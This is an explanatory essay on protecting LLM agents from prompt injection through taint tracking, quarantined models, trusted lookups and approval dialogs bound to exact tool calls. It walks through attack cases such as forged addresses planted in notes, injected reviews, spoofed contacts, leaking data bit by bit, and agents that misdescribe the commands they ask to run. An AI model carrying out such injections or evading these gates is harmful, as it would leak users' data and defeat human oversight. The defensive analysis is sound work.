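In CaMeL, the planner turns the user's request into a complete program before the agent reads any data. According to Willison, the designers chose a restricted version of Python for the program because language models already write Python well. A custom interpreter breaks the program into a tree of operations and evaluates them one by one, so it can record which variables derive from which others. It also attaches tags called capabilities to values. These hold much the same information as labels, such as a value's source and who may read it.

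In Willison's example, a program takes Bob's address from the latest email and sends him a reminder about a meeting. Fetching email is always allowed, but sending requires a trusted recipient, and the system can ask the user about an unknown one. The program also requires the quarantined model's answer to be formatted as an email address. This keeps stray text out of the recipient field, but a forged address would still pass the format check.

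The planner never receives a tool result, so its context stays trusted for the whole run and an address typed by the user stays usable. Willison points out that this also helps privacy, because the company hosting the planner receives only the user's request. The quarantined model's task is easier, so that model can be smaller, perhaps small enough to run on the user's own computer, and private data might then never leave that computer.

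The disadvantage is that the planner has to write a program that works without seeing the data. This is fine for Bob's request, because the same steps in the same order are right whatever the notes contain. Costa and colleagues call such tasks data independent. A request to complete today's tasks in a to-do app is data dependent, since the agent can't choose its tools until it knows what the tasks are. Stanley, Verma and colleagues (2026) say in *An AI Agent Execution Environment to Safeguard User Data* that CaMeL completes fewer tasks because it does not let the planner revise the program after seeing intermediate results.

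### FIDES hides untrusted results as it goes

FIDES keeps the ordinary loop, in which the planner makes a call, looks at what comes back and decides on the next one. Two functions control what the planner sees and what the tools receive. In simplified form:

```
HIDE(value, label):
    if label is not ⊑ context_label:
        store (value, label) in memory under a new name, and return the name
    if value is a record or a list:
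        return it with HIDE applied to each of its parts
    return value

EXPAND(arguments):
    replace each variable name with its stored value and its stored label
    leave literals as they are, with the label of the call
```

`HIDE` runs on every tool result before the planner sees it. It hides only the parts that would raise the context label. For example, if `find_notes` returns a record with a trusted date and an untrusted text, the planner might receive this:

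```
{date: "2 October", text: #find_notes-result-0.text#}
```

The planner can read the date but sees only a variable name in place of the text. To get Bob's address, it passes that name to the quarantined model, which reads the text and puts the address in another hidden variable. The planner then writes a `send_email` call with the new variable's name as the recipient. Just before the gate, `EXPAND` replaces the name with the actual address and its untrusted label, so the call fails the trusted-recipient check, as it did in the table.

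Hiding only the data that would taint the context is as safe as hiding every tool result, as long as the labels are right, and it gives the planner more to work with. In an example from Costa and colleagues, a user asks the agent to find the chat channel with the fewest messages and add Alice to it. The channel names and messages are untrusted, so the planner sees variable names in their place, along with the length of each list of messages. It finds an empty list and passes the matching channel variable to the tool that adds Alice, without reading anything an outsider wrote.

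The example also shows that the executor's protection depends on its rule for each argument. The channel name came from an untrusted source, and anyone who can post can change which channel has the fewest messages. The call succeeded because the rule for that tool in these tests checked only the call's label. A rule requiring a trusted channel name would have blocked it.

#### Reading a hidden value

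For data-dependent tasks, the planner sometimes has to read a variable's contents. For example, a user might ask for a calendar event only if a recent email requests a meeting. The planner then has to learn something about the emails to decide. FIDES has an `inspect` tool that copies a variable's contents into the context and raises the context label to match. To limit the exposure, the planner can first have the quarantined model reduce the email to a yes or no, then inspect only that answer.

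`HIDE` keeps a new result from the planner only if the result's label exceeds the current context label. Inspecting ordinary untrusted text makes the context label untrusted, so `HIDE` passes later untrusted results straight to the planner. From then on, FIDES protects the planner's context from injections no better than an ordinary agent does, and only the gate can still block a harmful call prompted by an injected instruction.

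#### Separate labels for the call and its arguments

The call's label records what the planner had read when it chose the tool, and each argument's label records where that value came from. In an ordinary agent these labels are always the same, because the planner writes every argument itself. They can differ in FIDES because the planner can pass on a value it has not read.

Suppose a user asks the agent to search the web and send a summary to a colleague whose address is in the request. The call and the recipient are trusted, but the message body is untrusted. In Bob's case, the call is trusted but the recipient is untrusted. If the executor gave each call a single combined label, both calls would be untrusted, and it would have to allow both or block both. With separate labels, it can send the summary and block the email to the address from the notes.

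A call can be untrusted even when one of its arguments is trusted. FIDES can hide confidential data in variables as well as untrusted data, so a variable may hold a payroll file that only the company's own staff could have written. If the planner then inspects an email with an injected instruction to send that file somewhere, the file is still labeled trusted, but the call is labeled untrusted because an outsider may have prompted it.

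### GAAP tracks branches, new plans and later tasks

The planner's program can also leak data without copying it. Suppose a plan reads a salary file and then branches:

```
1  salary = read_file("salary.txt")
2  if salary > 100000, go to 3, otherwise go to 4
3  send_email(to="ana@example.com", body="Yes")
4  print("Done")
```

Ana can learn something about the salary from whether the email arrives, even though the word "Yes" contains nothing from the file. GAAP, the execution environment that Stanley and colleagues built, catches this by analysing the generated plan. For each branch, it finds the first later instruction that every path must reach, which here is line 4. It then taints every instruction between the branch and that point with the data used in the condition. If there is a loop, it taints everything in the loop. The email in line 3 therefore counts as sharing `salary.txt` with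 Ana, and it goes out only if the user has permitted that. Without permission, no email goes out whatever the salary is, so Ana learns nothing from its absence.

A refusal could also reveal information to a plan. When GAAP blocks a call, it continues the run and returns an error with the same taint a normal result would have had, so any later step that depends on the error is tainted too.

GAAP's plans use a very small custom language. Each numbered instruction is either a tool call or a branch, and it can refer to earlier results by number. Stanley and colleagues argue that existing taint trackers for standard Python aren't reliable enough to enforce security, because they were built to find bugs and Python has too many complex features to cover. Tracking data completely is much easier in a language with only two kinds of instruction.

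GAAP protects only confidentiality. It checks whether the user has allowed a particular item of private data to go to a particular party, and it doesn't label data as trusted or untrusted. Its guarantee holds even if an attacker controls the planner. For an email, a short description of the tool, called an annotation, identifies the party as whoever is in the recipient field. In Bob's case, GAAP would look for permission to share `budget.pdf` with the exact address from the notes. If the address were forged, it would find no permission and would stop to ask the user. It would also ask about Bob's real address the first time. GAAP wouldn't stop an injection that deletes files without sharing anything.

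#### Writing a new plan partway through

A GAAP plan can return selected results to the planner, which then writes a new plan. The taints on those results apply to every call in the new plan. This is context taint again, but it comes only from the results that the earlier plan returned.

In one example, the user asks the agent to email a file to Alice and, if that works, to do the task described in the file. The first plan sends the file, has the quarantined model check whether the email succeeded, and then gives the file to the planner. The executor treats every later call as sharing that file. If an attacker had written the file, the planner would be reading the attacker's instructions, and GAAP would limit only where private data could go.

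Even with replanning, the planner has to write many instructions before it knows what the data looks like. In one test, the plan had the quarantined model find the most recent email about resetting a password. The model picked an email from an unsafe sender, and the plan used it without any further check. In another test, the planner had told the agent never to repeat a checkout. When the shop asked for a one-time code and a second attempt, the agent didn't try again. Stanley and colleagues attribute failures of this type, about 4% of all tasks, to GAAP's structure. CaMeL's planner has the same problem and can't replan.

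#### Remembering what has already been shared

GAAP also keeps taints from one task to the next. Suppose the agent gives an airline the user's passport number to check in for a flight. A few days later, the user asks the agent to email the airline's confirmation to a friend. The confirmation may contain the passport number, although nothing in the second task mentions it.

GAAP logs every item it shares and with whom. When the agent later gets data from the same service, the executor treats that data as possibly including anything the service has received. Developers can narrow this with annotations. For example, a food-ordering service might repeat the list of dishes in its reply but never the password, so the developer can exclude the password from the taint. A wrong exclusion would let private data through unlabelled, so Stanley and colleagues want annotations to be public and open to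 checking, with the most cautious assumption as the default.

### Inferring which inputs mattered

The systems so far assume that anything the planner read could have affected what it wrote, which is safe but often wrong. A user might ask for a summary of the meeting notes and then type, "Email ana@example.com that I'm running late." In an ordinary agent, the notes taint the second request even though they are irrelevant to it. Several systems try to infer which inputs affected the planner's output, so that it can read freely without tainting everything it writes afterwards.

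#### Removing what seems irrelevant

An early method by Siddiqui and colleagues looks for a smaller set of inputs that produces a similar answer. It then regenerates the answer from that set, so the answer needs only the labels of the remaining inputs. Zhong and colleagues estimate that this takes 16 to 64 extra model calls for a typical lattice with four to six levels.

Their own system, RTBAS, replaces the search with a prediction, and works as follows:

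1. A screener marks the parts of the conversation that seem relevant to the next step.
2. The executor combines the labels of those parts into one label.
3. It removes every part of the conversation whose label exceeds the combined one.
4. The planner writes its next tool call from what is left.
5. The gate checks the combined label against the tool's limit and asks the user if the call fails.

For the message to Ana, the screener should mark only the user's request as relevant. The executor then removes the notes, and the call is trusted. If the screener also marks the notes by mistake, the user gets an unnecessary question. If it misses something the planner needs, the planner has to work without it.

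Zhong and colleagues say that the screener's mistakes therefore can't compromise security. This holds for copied text, because the planner can only use text that the combined label covers. The screener reads the attacker's text, so an attacker might influence what it keeps, but any text it keeps still counts towards the label. The protection depends entirely on the removal in step 3. In the published pseudocode, the planner appears to receive the full conversation when it writes its reply to the user, although the definitions call for the shortened one. An implementation that copied this could store a tainted reply under a trusted label.

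RTBAS gives each call a single label, so it can't distinguish a trusted recipient from an untrusted body. If the user asks the agent to email a summary of untrusted notes to `ana@example.com`, the notes are relevant to the call, so the whole call needs confirmation. FIDES would allow the call under a rule that requires only the recipient to be trusted.

The screener has two versions. In one, the executor prompts a second language model to pick out the relevant parts of the conversation. The other uses attention scores, which estimate how much harder the output would be to predict without a given piece of the input. A small neural network turns these scores into a decision about each part.

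Computing the scores requires access to a model's internals, which commercial models don't provide, so Zhong and colleagues used small open models to estimate what had influenced the large ones. The scores only partly separate relevant from irrelevant data. Between 74% and 86% of the scores for unrelated data fell below 0.2, but so did 14% of the scores for related data in conversations with GPT-4o and 44% in conversations with Claude. On a set of hand-labeled privacy tasks, the language-model screener gave exactly the right label about 70% of the time. The attention version was right 57% of the time, which was no real improvement on assuming that every call used all the private data in the context.

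#### Matching text after the fact

Other systems estimate influence without removing anything. *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Tang and colleagues, 2026) presents NeuroTaint, which searches the record of a finished run for links between untrusted sources and sensitive calls. It starts with the check that takes the least computation. During the run, NeuroTaint adds a unique random marker to the text each source returns, and if that marker appears in a later argument, the link is certain. Next it looks for overlapping text, and then for similar meaning, first across the whole source and then in smaller pieces.

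If none of these finds a link, a language model compares the original conversation with a version that replaces the suspect text with a neutral placeholder, such as a message that the search found nothing. If the model judges that the agent would not have made the call in the second version, NeuroTaint reports a link. This can catch cases that argument labels miss. For example, a fake policy email might cause an agent to forward a customer's message to an attacker, even though the forwarded message contains none of the email's text.

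NeuroTaint also saves its records between sessions, so it can connect a document the agent stored on Monday with a report it wrote on Thursday. It would probably link Bob's address to the meeting notes easily, because the address appears in both places. Text that has been paraphrased several times is harder to trace. In 400 test scenarios, half of which contained a real link, NeuroTaint missed 13 links and raised 16 false alarms. Ten of the missed links depended on similar meaning, mostly after repeated rewording.

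These are good results for an audit, which is what NeuroTaint is for. It would be weaker as a gate, because each kind of similarity has a fixed threshold and an attacker who knew the thresholds could try to stay below them. Cai and colleagues also compare NeuroTaint with FIDES, and count a false alarm whenever FIDES flags a path that carried no harmful content. In a gate, such a false alarm would be an unnecessary refusal, which is a real drawback but doesn't let an attack through.

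#### Asking the planner where a value came from

In *Agent-Sentry* (2026), Sequeira, Damianakis and colleagues add fields to each tool's arguments in which the planner must state where every value came from and whether it copied, derived or made up the value. The system removes these fields before the tool runs. The method works with an existing agent and needs no changes to its tools.

Sequeira and colleagues don't fully trust these reports, with good reason, since a planner that has obeyed an injection also writes the reports. If the planner reports copying an address from the user's request, ordinary code could search the request for that address. Code has no such test for a value that the planner reports deriving from several sources.

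Agent-Sentry combines the reports with other evidence. A classifier trained on earlier legitimate runs allows or blocks the clear cases. A list of known values from trusted sources settles some of the rest, and a language model compares any remaining calls with the user's request. A new address for Bob, taken from the notes, could easily reach that last check. The user asked the agent to email Bob, so a forged address might look consistent with the request.

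Inference makes agents easier to use because the planner can read what it needs and harmless calls are less likely to fail. But if the executor lowers a label based on a prediction, an attacker only has to cause one wrong prediction at the right moment. RTBAS avoids this for copied text by acting on the prediction before the planner writes anything. An executor can safely use a prediction to choose what to remove from the planner's context, but it shouldn't use one to clear the taint from a call after the planner has read the text.

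## Supplying a blocked value without asking a person

When the gate refuses to send Bob's document, the plan needs only an address that no outsider could have written. The executor can report the refusal to the planner, as FIDES did in its tests, and let the planner correct that one argument. The error message should identify the argument and the rule but leave out the blocked address, because the planner will read whatever the message contains.

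The best replacement is the same value from a trusted source. If none exists, the quarantined model may be able to choose from a list of acceptable values. A planner that knows the rules in advance can use either method from the start and avoid the refusal.

### Looking the value up in a trusted source

Bob's address is probably in the user's address book as well as in the meeting notes. The planner can drop the line that extracted the address from the notes and look Bob up instead:

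```
bob = find_contact("Bob")
send_email(to=bob.email, attachments=document)
```

The name "Bob" comes from the user's request and outsiders can't write to the address book, so the address is trusted and the email goes out. A forged address in the notes no longer matters, because the new plan never uses it. The name has to be trusted too, because an address looked up using a name from the notes would be untrusted.

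A bank's list of saved payees can serve the same purpose for payments, but a lookup may supply only some of the arguments. *ARGUS* (2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to pay the latest electricity bill. The supplier's account may be among the saved payees, but this month's amount is only in the bill.

#### Two Bobs

The gate can't catch a wrong choice between two Bobs in the address book, so the lookup should fail unless exactly one contact matches. Nylas' developer guide *How to search contacts* describes an address-book service that can't search by name. The developer's code has to fetch a list of contacts, 30 at a time by default, and compare the names itself. Code that checks only the first 30 could find one Bob, miss the other and treat the match as unique.

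Other trusted data may show which Bob the user means. If the user invited only one of the Bobs to the meeting, and nobody else could edit the guest list, ordinary code can pick that one. Otherwise, the executor can compare both Bobs' addresses with the one in the notes and use whichever matches. An attacker who edits the notes could then choose between the Bobs but couldn't make the executor use any other address.

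#### Contacts created from incoming mail

Some software adds contacts automatically, so an attacker could set their display name to "Bob" and email the user, and the software would save that name with the attacker's address.

Nylas keeps contacts the user can edit in a source called `address_book` and contacts derived from the user's mail in a separate source called `inbox`. A trusted lookup should use only `address_book`. Even that isn't always safe, because Nylas' *Parse email addresses to enrich contacts* recommends saving addresses from messages to `address_book`. Nylas' *How Agent Account contacts work* describes an agent that saves every new correspondent as a contact when a message arrives, and another Nylas guide suggests using an agent's contacts as the list of people it may write to. If a developer did both, anyone could join that list by emailing the agent.

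Ignoring senders doesn't solve the problem. The mail client Pony collects contacts from the To and Cc lines of every message it indexes, but not from the From line. An attacker can still put a second address of their own in the Cc line under the name "Bob".

The developer should treat creating or changing a contact as a sensitive action, with both the name and the address as guarded arguments. Alternatively, the developer can store each contact with its label, as for the agent's memory, so that the lookup can skip contacts that came from incoming mail.

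### Letting the quarantined model choose from a list

Suppose the user had written, "Send the budget to whoever asked for it in our last meeting." Only the notes can identify that person, but the planner can still limit the answer to the eight contacts in the user's address book. It can give the quarantined model the notes and the contacts' addresses, and require it to return one of those addresses.

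FIDES's design enforces such limits with constrained decoding, in which the software running the model rules out any token that would break the required format. The model then can't return a ninth address, even if the notes contain an instruction to do so. The executor adds the answer's type to its label. Types form a lattice, ordered by how much information a value can carry:

```
bool  ⊑  enum["a", "b", "c"]  ⊑  string
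```

A Boolean (`bool`) is a yes or a no, an enumeration (`enum`) is one option from a fixed list, and a string can be any text. A yes-or-no answer drawn from untrusted public data has the label `((U, L), bool)`. A developer could write a rule that accepts an untrusted recipient if it is an enumeration, but not if it is a string. Costa and colleagues reason that a value with few possible options is a poor way to deliver an injected instruction or carry stolen data out.

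The options must come from trusted data. If the planner offered addresses extracted from the notes, the answer would still be a choice from a fixed list, but the forged address would be on that list.

Costa and colleagues left constrained decoding out of their tests. Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025) built and tested agents on a similar principle in *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*. Their quarantined model can pass the planner only integers, decimal numbers, Booleans and choices from a list. In their shopping agent, it rates each product review from 0 to 10 on relevance and on how strongly the review supports the product. The planner receives the median scores and the number of reviews, so a single malicious review has little effect when there are many others.

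Injected reviews turned the unprotected shopping agent away from the right product 31.7% of the time, but never succeeded against the protected agent. The protected agent also completed about as many purchases correctly (22.4%, compared with 21.8% for the unprotected one). The restriction did more harm to an agent that fixes software bugs. Its planner received the type and likely location of each bug instead of the written report, and the agent's success rate fell from 68.3% to 45.0%. Jacob and colleagues say the rate fell because the reports' wording is important.

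#### Counting the bits

A choice among `n` options carries `log2(n)` bits of information:

```
one of 8 contacts:        log2(8)        =    3 bits
one yes-or-no answer:     log2(2)        =    1 bit
100 yes-or-no answers:    100 × log2(2)  =  100 bits
```

With 3 bits, an attacker who controls the notes can pick the wrong contact but can't introduce a new address. Introducing `attacker@example.com` takes 100 bits, because it has 20 characters and each takes 5 bits in an alphabet of 32 (the 26 letters and six others, including "@" and the full stop).

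A planner could assemble such an address simply to complete the user's task. After the executor blocks a call, the planner might prompt the quarantined model to pick the first character of Bob's address from a list of 32, then the second, and so on. If the rules let the planner read small enumerations without tainting its context, it could write the finished address into `send_email` as a literal, and the executor would label the address as trusted.

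The type lattice doesn't limit how much information many answers can carry in total, because joining labels doesn't add up their capacities. Since `bool ⊔ bool = bool`, a hundred yes-or-no answers joined together have the same type as one. The executor therefore needs a separate counter for the whole run, which adds `log2(n)` bits for each answer it releases with `n` possible values and stops at a maximum. With a maximum of 10 bits, the quarantined model could choose among eight contacts at most three times. Jacob and colleagues similarly limit the length of lists because a long list of numbers could encode text. Integers need a limit as well, because a single 31-digit number can carry more than 100 bits.

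The counter also has to keep running when the agent retries a task. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) describes a leak of this kind in CaMeL, whose interpreter runs inside an ordinary loop that retries failed programs. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can reveal one bit of a secret, and the loop doesn't track that bit, so repeated attempts could reveal the whole secret.

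#### When one bit is too many

The number of bits measures how many outcomes an attacker can choose from, but not how bad the worst one is. Suppose a user asks an agent to pay a builder if the meeting notes confirm that the work is finished. The answer is only one bit, but a false "yes" sends the money. Choosing one of 1,024 files takes only 10 bits, but an attacker could use them to pick the payroll file.

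A developer should therefore check that every option on the list would be acceptable even if an attacker chose it. In Bob's case, this means removing any contact who must not see the budget and any file that must not leave the company. If a wrong "yes" would trigger a large payment, no untrusted answer, however short, should decide whether to pay.

Garby and colleagues also object that exceptions for small values are hard to audit. When such a value passes the gate, nobody can tell from that run whether it was a harmless exception or a real leak. In LLMbda, their programming language for agents, a programmer has to mark each exception with an `endorse` operation, so a reviewer can find every use of it in the code. `endorse` can raise a value's integrity without changing who may read it.

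### Planning around the rules

In FIDES, the planner isn't given the security rules, so it may choose a plan that the gate will reject even when an acceptable one exists. Kolluri and colleagues built PRUDENTIA on top of FIDES to avoid this. Each tool's description includes its policy, and the planner's instructions explain the labels, warn that reading a hidden variable can permanently taint the context, and tell the planner to make any guarded calls it can before reading untrusted text.

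Before reading a hidden variable, the planner is supposed to call a tool named `ifc_plan` and explain:

- why it needs the contents and what it expects to find
- why the quarantined model can't do the job
- which later calls would then need a person's approval.

The tool only records this explanation, and no code checks whether the reasons are good. The gate is unchanged, so a poor plan can cause a failed task or an unnecessary question to the user, but it can't get a forbidden call through.

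In one recorded run, a user asked for a summary of a day's appointments and a password reset link. The planner noted that, after reading the hidden text, it wouldn't need any guarded tools. It read the appointment descriptions, found the email and gave the user the link without requesting approval. The search had also returned a message from a suspicious AOL address. Because the gate doesn't check replies to the user, an instruction hidden in an appointment could have led the planner to show a link from that message instead.

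For Bob's document, a planner told that the recipient must be trusted would look up his address in the address book from the start. PRUDENTIA's planner might not, because its tool descriptions include only the rules for the planner's context, not those for individual arguments. Its instructions also encourage it to pass the quarantined model's answers directly to tools, which is how Bob's forged address reached `send_email`. A developer who guards individual arguments should therefore include those rules in the tool descriptions too.

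### Requests that none of these methods can complete

In a data-independent task, the same calls work whatever the data contains. If `solutions(d)` is the set of sequences of tool calls and final responses that work for data `d`, Costa and colleagues' formal definition requires at least one sequence to be in every set:

```
solutions(d1) ∩ solutions(d2) ∩ ...  ≠  ∅
```

Forwarding the three latest emails to a colleague meets this definition, because the planner can pass the emails on as hidden variables. Tasks that don't meet the definition are data dependent.

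Bob's request counts as data independent even though the gate blocks it, because the definition doesn't consider whether each argument comes from a trusted source. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) sorts requests by how much the user specifies. Some requests give both the action and its values, some give only the action, and others leave both to what the agent reads. Attacks succeeded much more often on requests that left the action open.

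| Request | What the untrusted data decides | What can help |
|---|---|---|
| "Send `budget.pdf` to bob@example.com." | Nothing | The gate already allows it. |
| "Send Bob the document he asked for." | The address and the file | An address-book lookup, and a choice from a list of safe files |
| "Send the budget to whoever asked for it." | The recipient | A choice from the user's contacts |
| "If an email asks for a meeting, add it to my calendar." | Whether to act, and the details | A yes-or-no answer, and a choice of guests from the user's contacts |
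| "Pay the invoice from our new supplier." | The account and the amount | None of these methods, if the invoice is the only source |
| "Do what Alice asked in her email." | The action and its values | None of these methods |

The calendar request needs limits on both the decision and the guests. Costa and colleagues' version limits only the decision. The quarantined model fills in the details without a fixed list, so an attacker could add a guest of their own.

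The request about Alice comes from *ARGUS*, which points out that an agent has nothing to do if it treats her email only as data. The address book can't supply her instructions. A fixed list of actions, such as scheduling a meeting or forwarding an email, would cover a few common requests, but each action would still need safe arguments. Knowing the rules doesn't help the planner either, because it can't make a plan until it has read the email. If an attacker adds text to that email, Alice's request and the attacker's carry the same label.

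Data-dependent tasks made up 5% of AgentDojo's office tasks, 10% of its travel tasks, 42.9% of its chat tasks and 43.8% of its banking tasks. Many of the banking tasks required the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, for example to schedule a payment, and FIDES blocked most of these tasks, as intended.

When the action or a guarded value exists only in untrusted text, and no short list of safe options can replace it, the executor has to refuse the call or ask the user. Such cases may be more common in practice than in tests. *AgentDyn* (2026) argues that agents can plan most benchmark tasks completely in advance, while real websites and messages contain many harmless instructions that agents need to follow, such as a request to log in before paying.

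## Asking a person to confirm the literal value

If Bob's address appears only in the meeting notes, the executor can stop before `send_email` and ask the user to approve that one call. The user's answer is useful only if they see the exact address the tool will receive and have some way to judge it.

Some values are easy for a user to judge. In an example from Zhong and colleagues, a user asks an agent to look up a recipe for lamingtons, an Australian cake, and buy any special ingredients. The shopping list has to come from a web page, so it is untrusted, but most people can see that icing sugar and desiccated coconut belong on it and that a gift card would not. An unfamiliar email address or bank account number is much harder to judge, so the dialog has to provide some context.

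### What the dialog should show

A poor dialog for Bob's address would look like this:

```
The assistant would like to email Bob the document he asked for.

[Cancel]   [OK]
```

The text is the same whether the address is real or forged, so the user can't tell the difference. If the planner writes the text, it may not be able to do any better, because in a dual-LLM design it has seen only the variable name `address`. The executor has the address, its label and the user's original request. Ordinary code can put these into a fixed template:

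```
Send budget.pdf to a new recipient?

To:            bob@example.com
Address from:  "Meeting notes, 2 October"
               People outside your company can edit these notes.
               This address is not in your contacts.
File:          budget.pdf, also named in the notes
New access:    Only you can open this file now.
               bob@example.com would receive a copy.
You asked:     "Send Bob the document he asked for in our last meeting."

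      [Don't send]   [Send budget.pdf to bob@example.com]
```

The executor already computes most of this. It gets the "New access" line by comparing the recipients with the file's permitted readers, as it does for the permitted flow rule. The "Address from" line requires a label that records the specific source, since a plain "untrusted" label can't identify the notes. Outsiders may be able to rename the notes and use the title to add a reassuring sentence to the dialog, so the template should put the title in quotation marks and limit its length.

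Microsoft also recommends showing where untrusted data came from, what the agent would share more widely, and with whom. Its sample policy for Teams messages falls a little short of this because it lists the new readers by user ID. The IDs are accurate, but Alex couldn't tell from a long string of letters and digits that one of the readers was Marco. The dialog should also show names from the company directory.

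AWS's *Get user confirmation before invoking action group function* describes how a developer can require confirmation for any action of an agent on Amazon's Bedrock service. Bedrock then sends the application the function, its arguments and a unique ID for the call, and the application returns the user's decision. The application can therefore display the literal values, whatever the agent writes in its own question.

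A person may not be able to judge an attachment by its name alone. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni et al., 2026) describes a user who asks an agent to reconcile supplier invoices and send an auditor only the summary totals. Injected text in a supplier's note leads the agent to copy the raw invoice rows into `report.csv`. When the agent asks to send that file, the auditor is an approved recipient and the file name looks ordinary, but the call would send the raw rows that the user wanted to withhold.

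The proposed interface tracks which files each new file was made from. It quotes the user's original instruction, displays the exact call, and shows just above the buttons that the attachment comes from raw invoice rows and would go to the auditor. The user can open the recorded events behind that statement, and the interface marks any missing evidence. It doesn't label the call a violation, so the user still has to compare the call with the instruction.

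### Consent Integrity

Weng (2026) defines what an approval has to guarantee, and calls it Consent Integrity, in *What You Approve Is What Executes*. The paper is about coding agents that ask the user before they run a command and write the description that the user approves. In 2025 the security company Checkmarx published an attack on such agents, Lies-in-the-Loop, in which a compromised agent describes a harmless action and runs a different one. According to Weng, the vendors that heard about the attack treated it as outside their threat models.

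Consent Integrity has four conditions:

1. Truthful rendering: a trusted program outside the agent writes the description from the real action and ignores the agent's account of it.
2. Faithfulness: the description includes every fact that matters for security, such as where data will go, whether the action reads passwords or keys, and whether it destroys anything permanently. This applies even if someone has disguised the command.
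3. A trusted path: the agent can't write in the dialog, cover it or answer it.
4. Binding to execution: the user's permission covers only the action in the description, and no other action can run under it.

For Bob's email, the executor meets the truthful rendering condition if it fills in the template from the actual arguments, which is fairly easy because `send_email` has a named argument for the recipient. The trusted path takes more work because the executor needs a separate window or device that the agent can't write to. In an ordinary chat window, a planner that has followed an injected instruction could print a fake dialog or surround the real one with misleading text.

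Faithfulness is much harder to achieve for shell commands, which can do almost anything. No program can work out the effects of every command, and compiled software is often opaque. Weng therefore proposes a weaker condition that a real system could meet. The analyser reports every fact it can reliably extract and marks any action it can't classify as uninspectable or high-risk. The dialog may show that an action is too obscure to explain, but it never presents such an action as safe.

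#### "What you see is what you sign"

The idea comes from digital signatures. Software computes a signature from a file's bytes, but the signer reads a picture of the file on a screen, and the two can differ. The principle of "what you see is what you sign" requires the display to match the content that the software signs. Some banking devices and hardware wallets, which hold the keys to cryptocurrency, apply this principle by sending transaction details directly from a protected chip to their own screen, so malicious software on the user's computer can't alter them.

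Weng identifies two complications in asking a person to confirm an agent's action. First, the agent, which an attacker may have compromised, normally describes the action. Second, the real action may be a low-level event, such as a network request, that a program has to translate before a person can understand it. A bank transfer needs little translation because the payer already understands the amount and payee.

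#### The EU payment rule

EU law applies the same principle to online payments. Article 5 of the European Commission's *Commission Delegated Regulation (EU) 2018/389* (2018) has the title "Dynamic linking" and covers the authentication code that confirms a payment. Banks and other payment providers must ensure that:

- the payer knows the amount and the payee
- the code is specific to that amount and payee
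- the code they accept matches the amount and payee that the payer agreed to
- any change to either one invalidates the code.

The European Commission justifies the rule by citing the higher risk of fraud in remote payments. Providers must also protect the information on the payer's screen from tampering, which resembles the trusted path condition. They may accept each code only once.

The European Banking Authority's *Definition of payee for dynamic linking* says the regulation doesn't specify how to identify a payee. A provider can use an IBAN (an international account number) or something similar, and can leave the IBAN out of the code's calculation if it meets the four requirements another way. An executor doesn't need this flexibility and should bind the approval to the whole email address, because two people's addresses can differ by a single character.

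Binding doesn't establish that the payee is the right one. If a forged invoice contains a thief's account number and the payer approves it, the payment can satisfy every part of Article 5. A separate rule helps by requiring euro-area providers to offer a check of the payee's name on euro transfers. It has applied since October 2025, according to The Paypers' *PSD3 and PSR clear ECON, fraud rules due from late 2028* (2026). For email, looking Bob up in the address book is a similar check. The directive behind Article 5 is due for replacement. The European Parliament has provisionally scheduled a vote for 14 December 2026, and most of the new provisions would apply from late 2028 or 2029.

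#### Binding an approval to a tool call

Weng's prototype binds approvals with a hash, a short fingerprint that changes if any part of the input changes. An executor could do the same for tool calls and add the single-use rule from payments:

```
when the user approves:
    approved = hash(tool, literal arguments, contents of attached files)
    used     = false

just before the tool runs:
    current = hash(tool, literal arguments, contents of attached files)
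    if current ≠ approved, or used is true:
        ask the user again
    otherwise:
        used = true
        run the tool with exactly these arguments and files
```

The hash has to cover the contents of `budget.pdf`, since another program could replace the file without changing its name. The single-use rule prevents an agent that is stuck in a loop from making the same payment twice on one approval.

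### How approvals fail

The table covers four common failures. The repairs for the summary and for the changed action follow Weng's design.

| What goes wrong | Repair |
|---|---|
| The agent writes the summary, so it can describe a different action. | The executor writes the summary from the actual call. If the agent's explanation appears too, the dialog labels it as unverified. |
| Harmless text pushes the important part out of view. | Guarded arguments always appear first, in full and in a fixed position. |
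| A display name or lookalike characters make a wrong address seem right. | The dialog shows the address itself, marks characters from unexpected alphabets and warns if the address resembles a known contact's. |
| The action changes after the user approves it. | The approval covers only the exact call, and any change triggers a new question. |

If the dialog cuts off a long address, it may hide the part that differs from the address the user expects. The executor should wrap long addresses over several lines and refuse any that are too long to display. The real destination can be even harder to spot in a URL.

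*Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use* (2026) includes a test with a misleading display name. A user asks an agent to reply to a colleague named Lisa Wong and attach a sales report. The inbox contains two messages signed with her name, and the more recent one comes from a Gmail address that resembles hers. An unprotected agent sent the report to the Gmail address. The paper's own agent got Lisa's address from the trusted contacts and then revealed only the message from that address, so it replied to the right person. If an approval dialog had shown only "Lisa Wong", the user could not have caught the mistake.

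Weng also considers encoded commands, which a person can't read even when the dialog shows them exactly. The prototype decodes them and shows the original text alongside a description of what they do. A short command can be just as obscure. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) gives the example of `python3 setup.py`, which looks routine but runs whatever code the file contains. Weng's prototype reads such a file before describing the command.

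### What the prototype caught and what it missed

Weng tested the prototype on commands from two public collections compiled by others. GTFOBins, which documents ways to misuse ordinary Unix programs, for example to read protected files, provided 1,330 commands. The tldr-pages project, which lists typical uses of command-line tools, provided 28,798.

| Prototype's response | Documented abuses | Ordinary commands |
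|---|---|---|
| Passed silently | 10.0% | 4.1% |
| Marked uninspectable | 59.5% | 87.0% |
| Reported a specific danger | 30.5% | 8.9% |

The prototype showed a prompt for 90.0% of the abuses and 95.9% of the ordinary commands, so users could infer almost nothing about a command's danger from seeing a prompt. The specific warnings were more informative because they appeared over three times as often for abuses as for ordinary commands. However, the tldr-pages collection covers 6,503 tools, many of them rare, so a developer who mostly uses a few familiar tools might see far fewer prompts.

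Most of these results depend on a list of trusted programs that can run without a prompt if the analyser finds nothing dangerous in the command. Every abuse that passed silently used a program on the list, and 83.4% of the ordinary commands were uninspectable only because their program wasn't on it. A longer list would mean fewer prompts but more silent abuses. Better analysis can help to some extent. When Weng added several checks, including one for writing to sensitive locations, silent passes fell from 15.0% to 10.0%.

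In 85 of the 133 silent passes, the command wrote to a temporary folder, and in eight it did something basic such as creating a folder. In another 19, it wrote files that would matter only if a later step used them. Weng counts the remaining 21 as real gaps in the analysis, such as ways to escape from a text editor into a shell.

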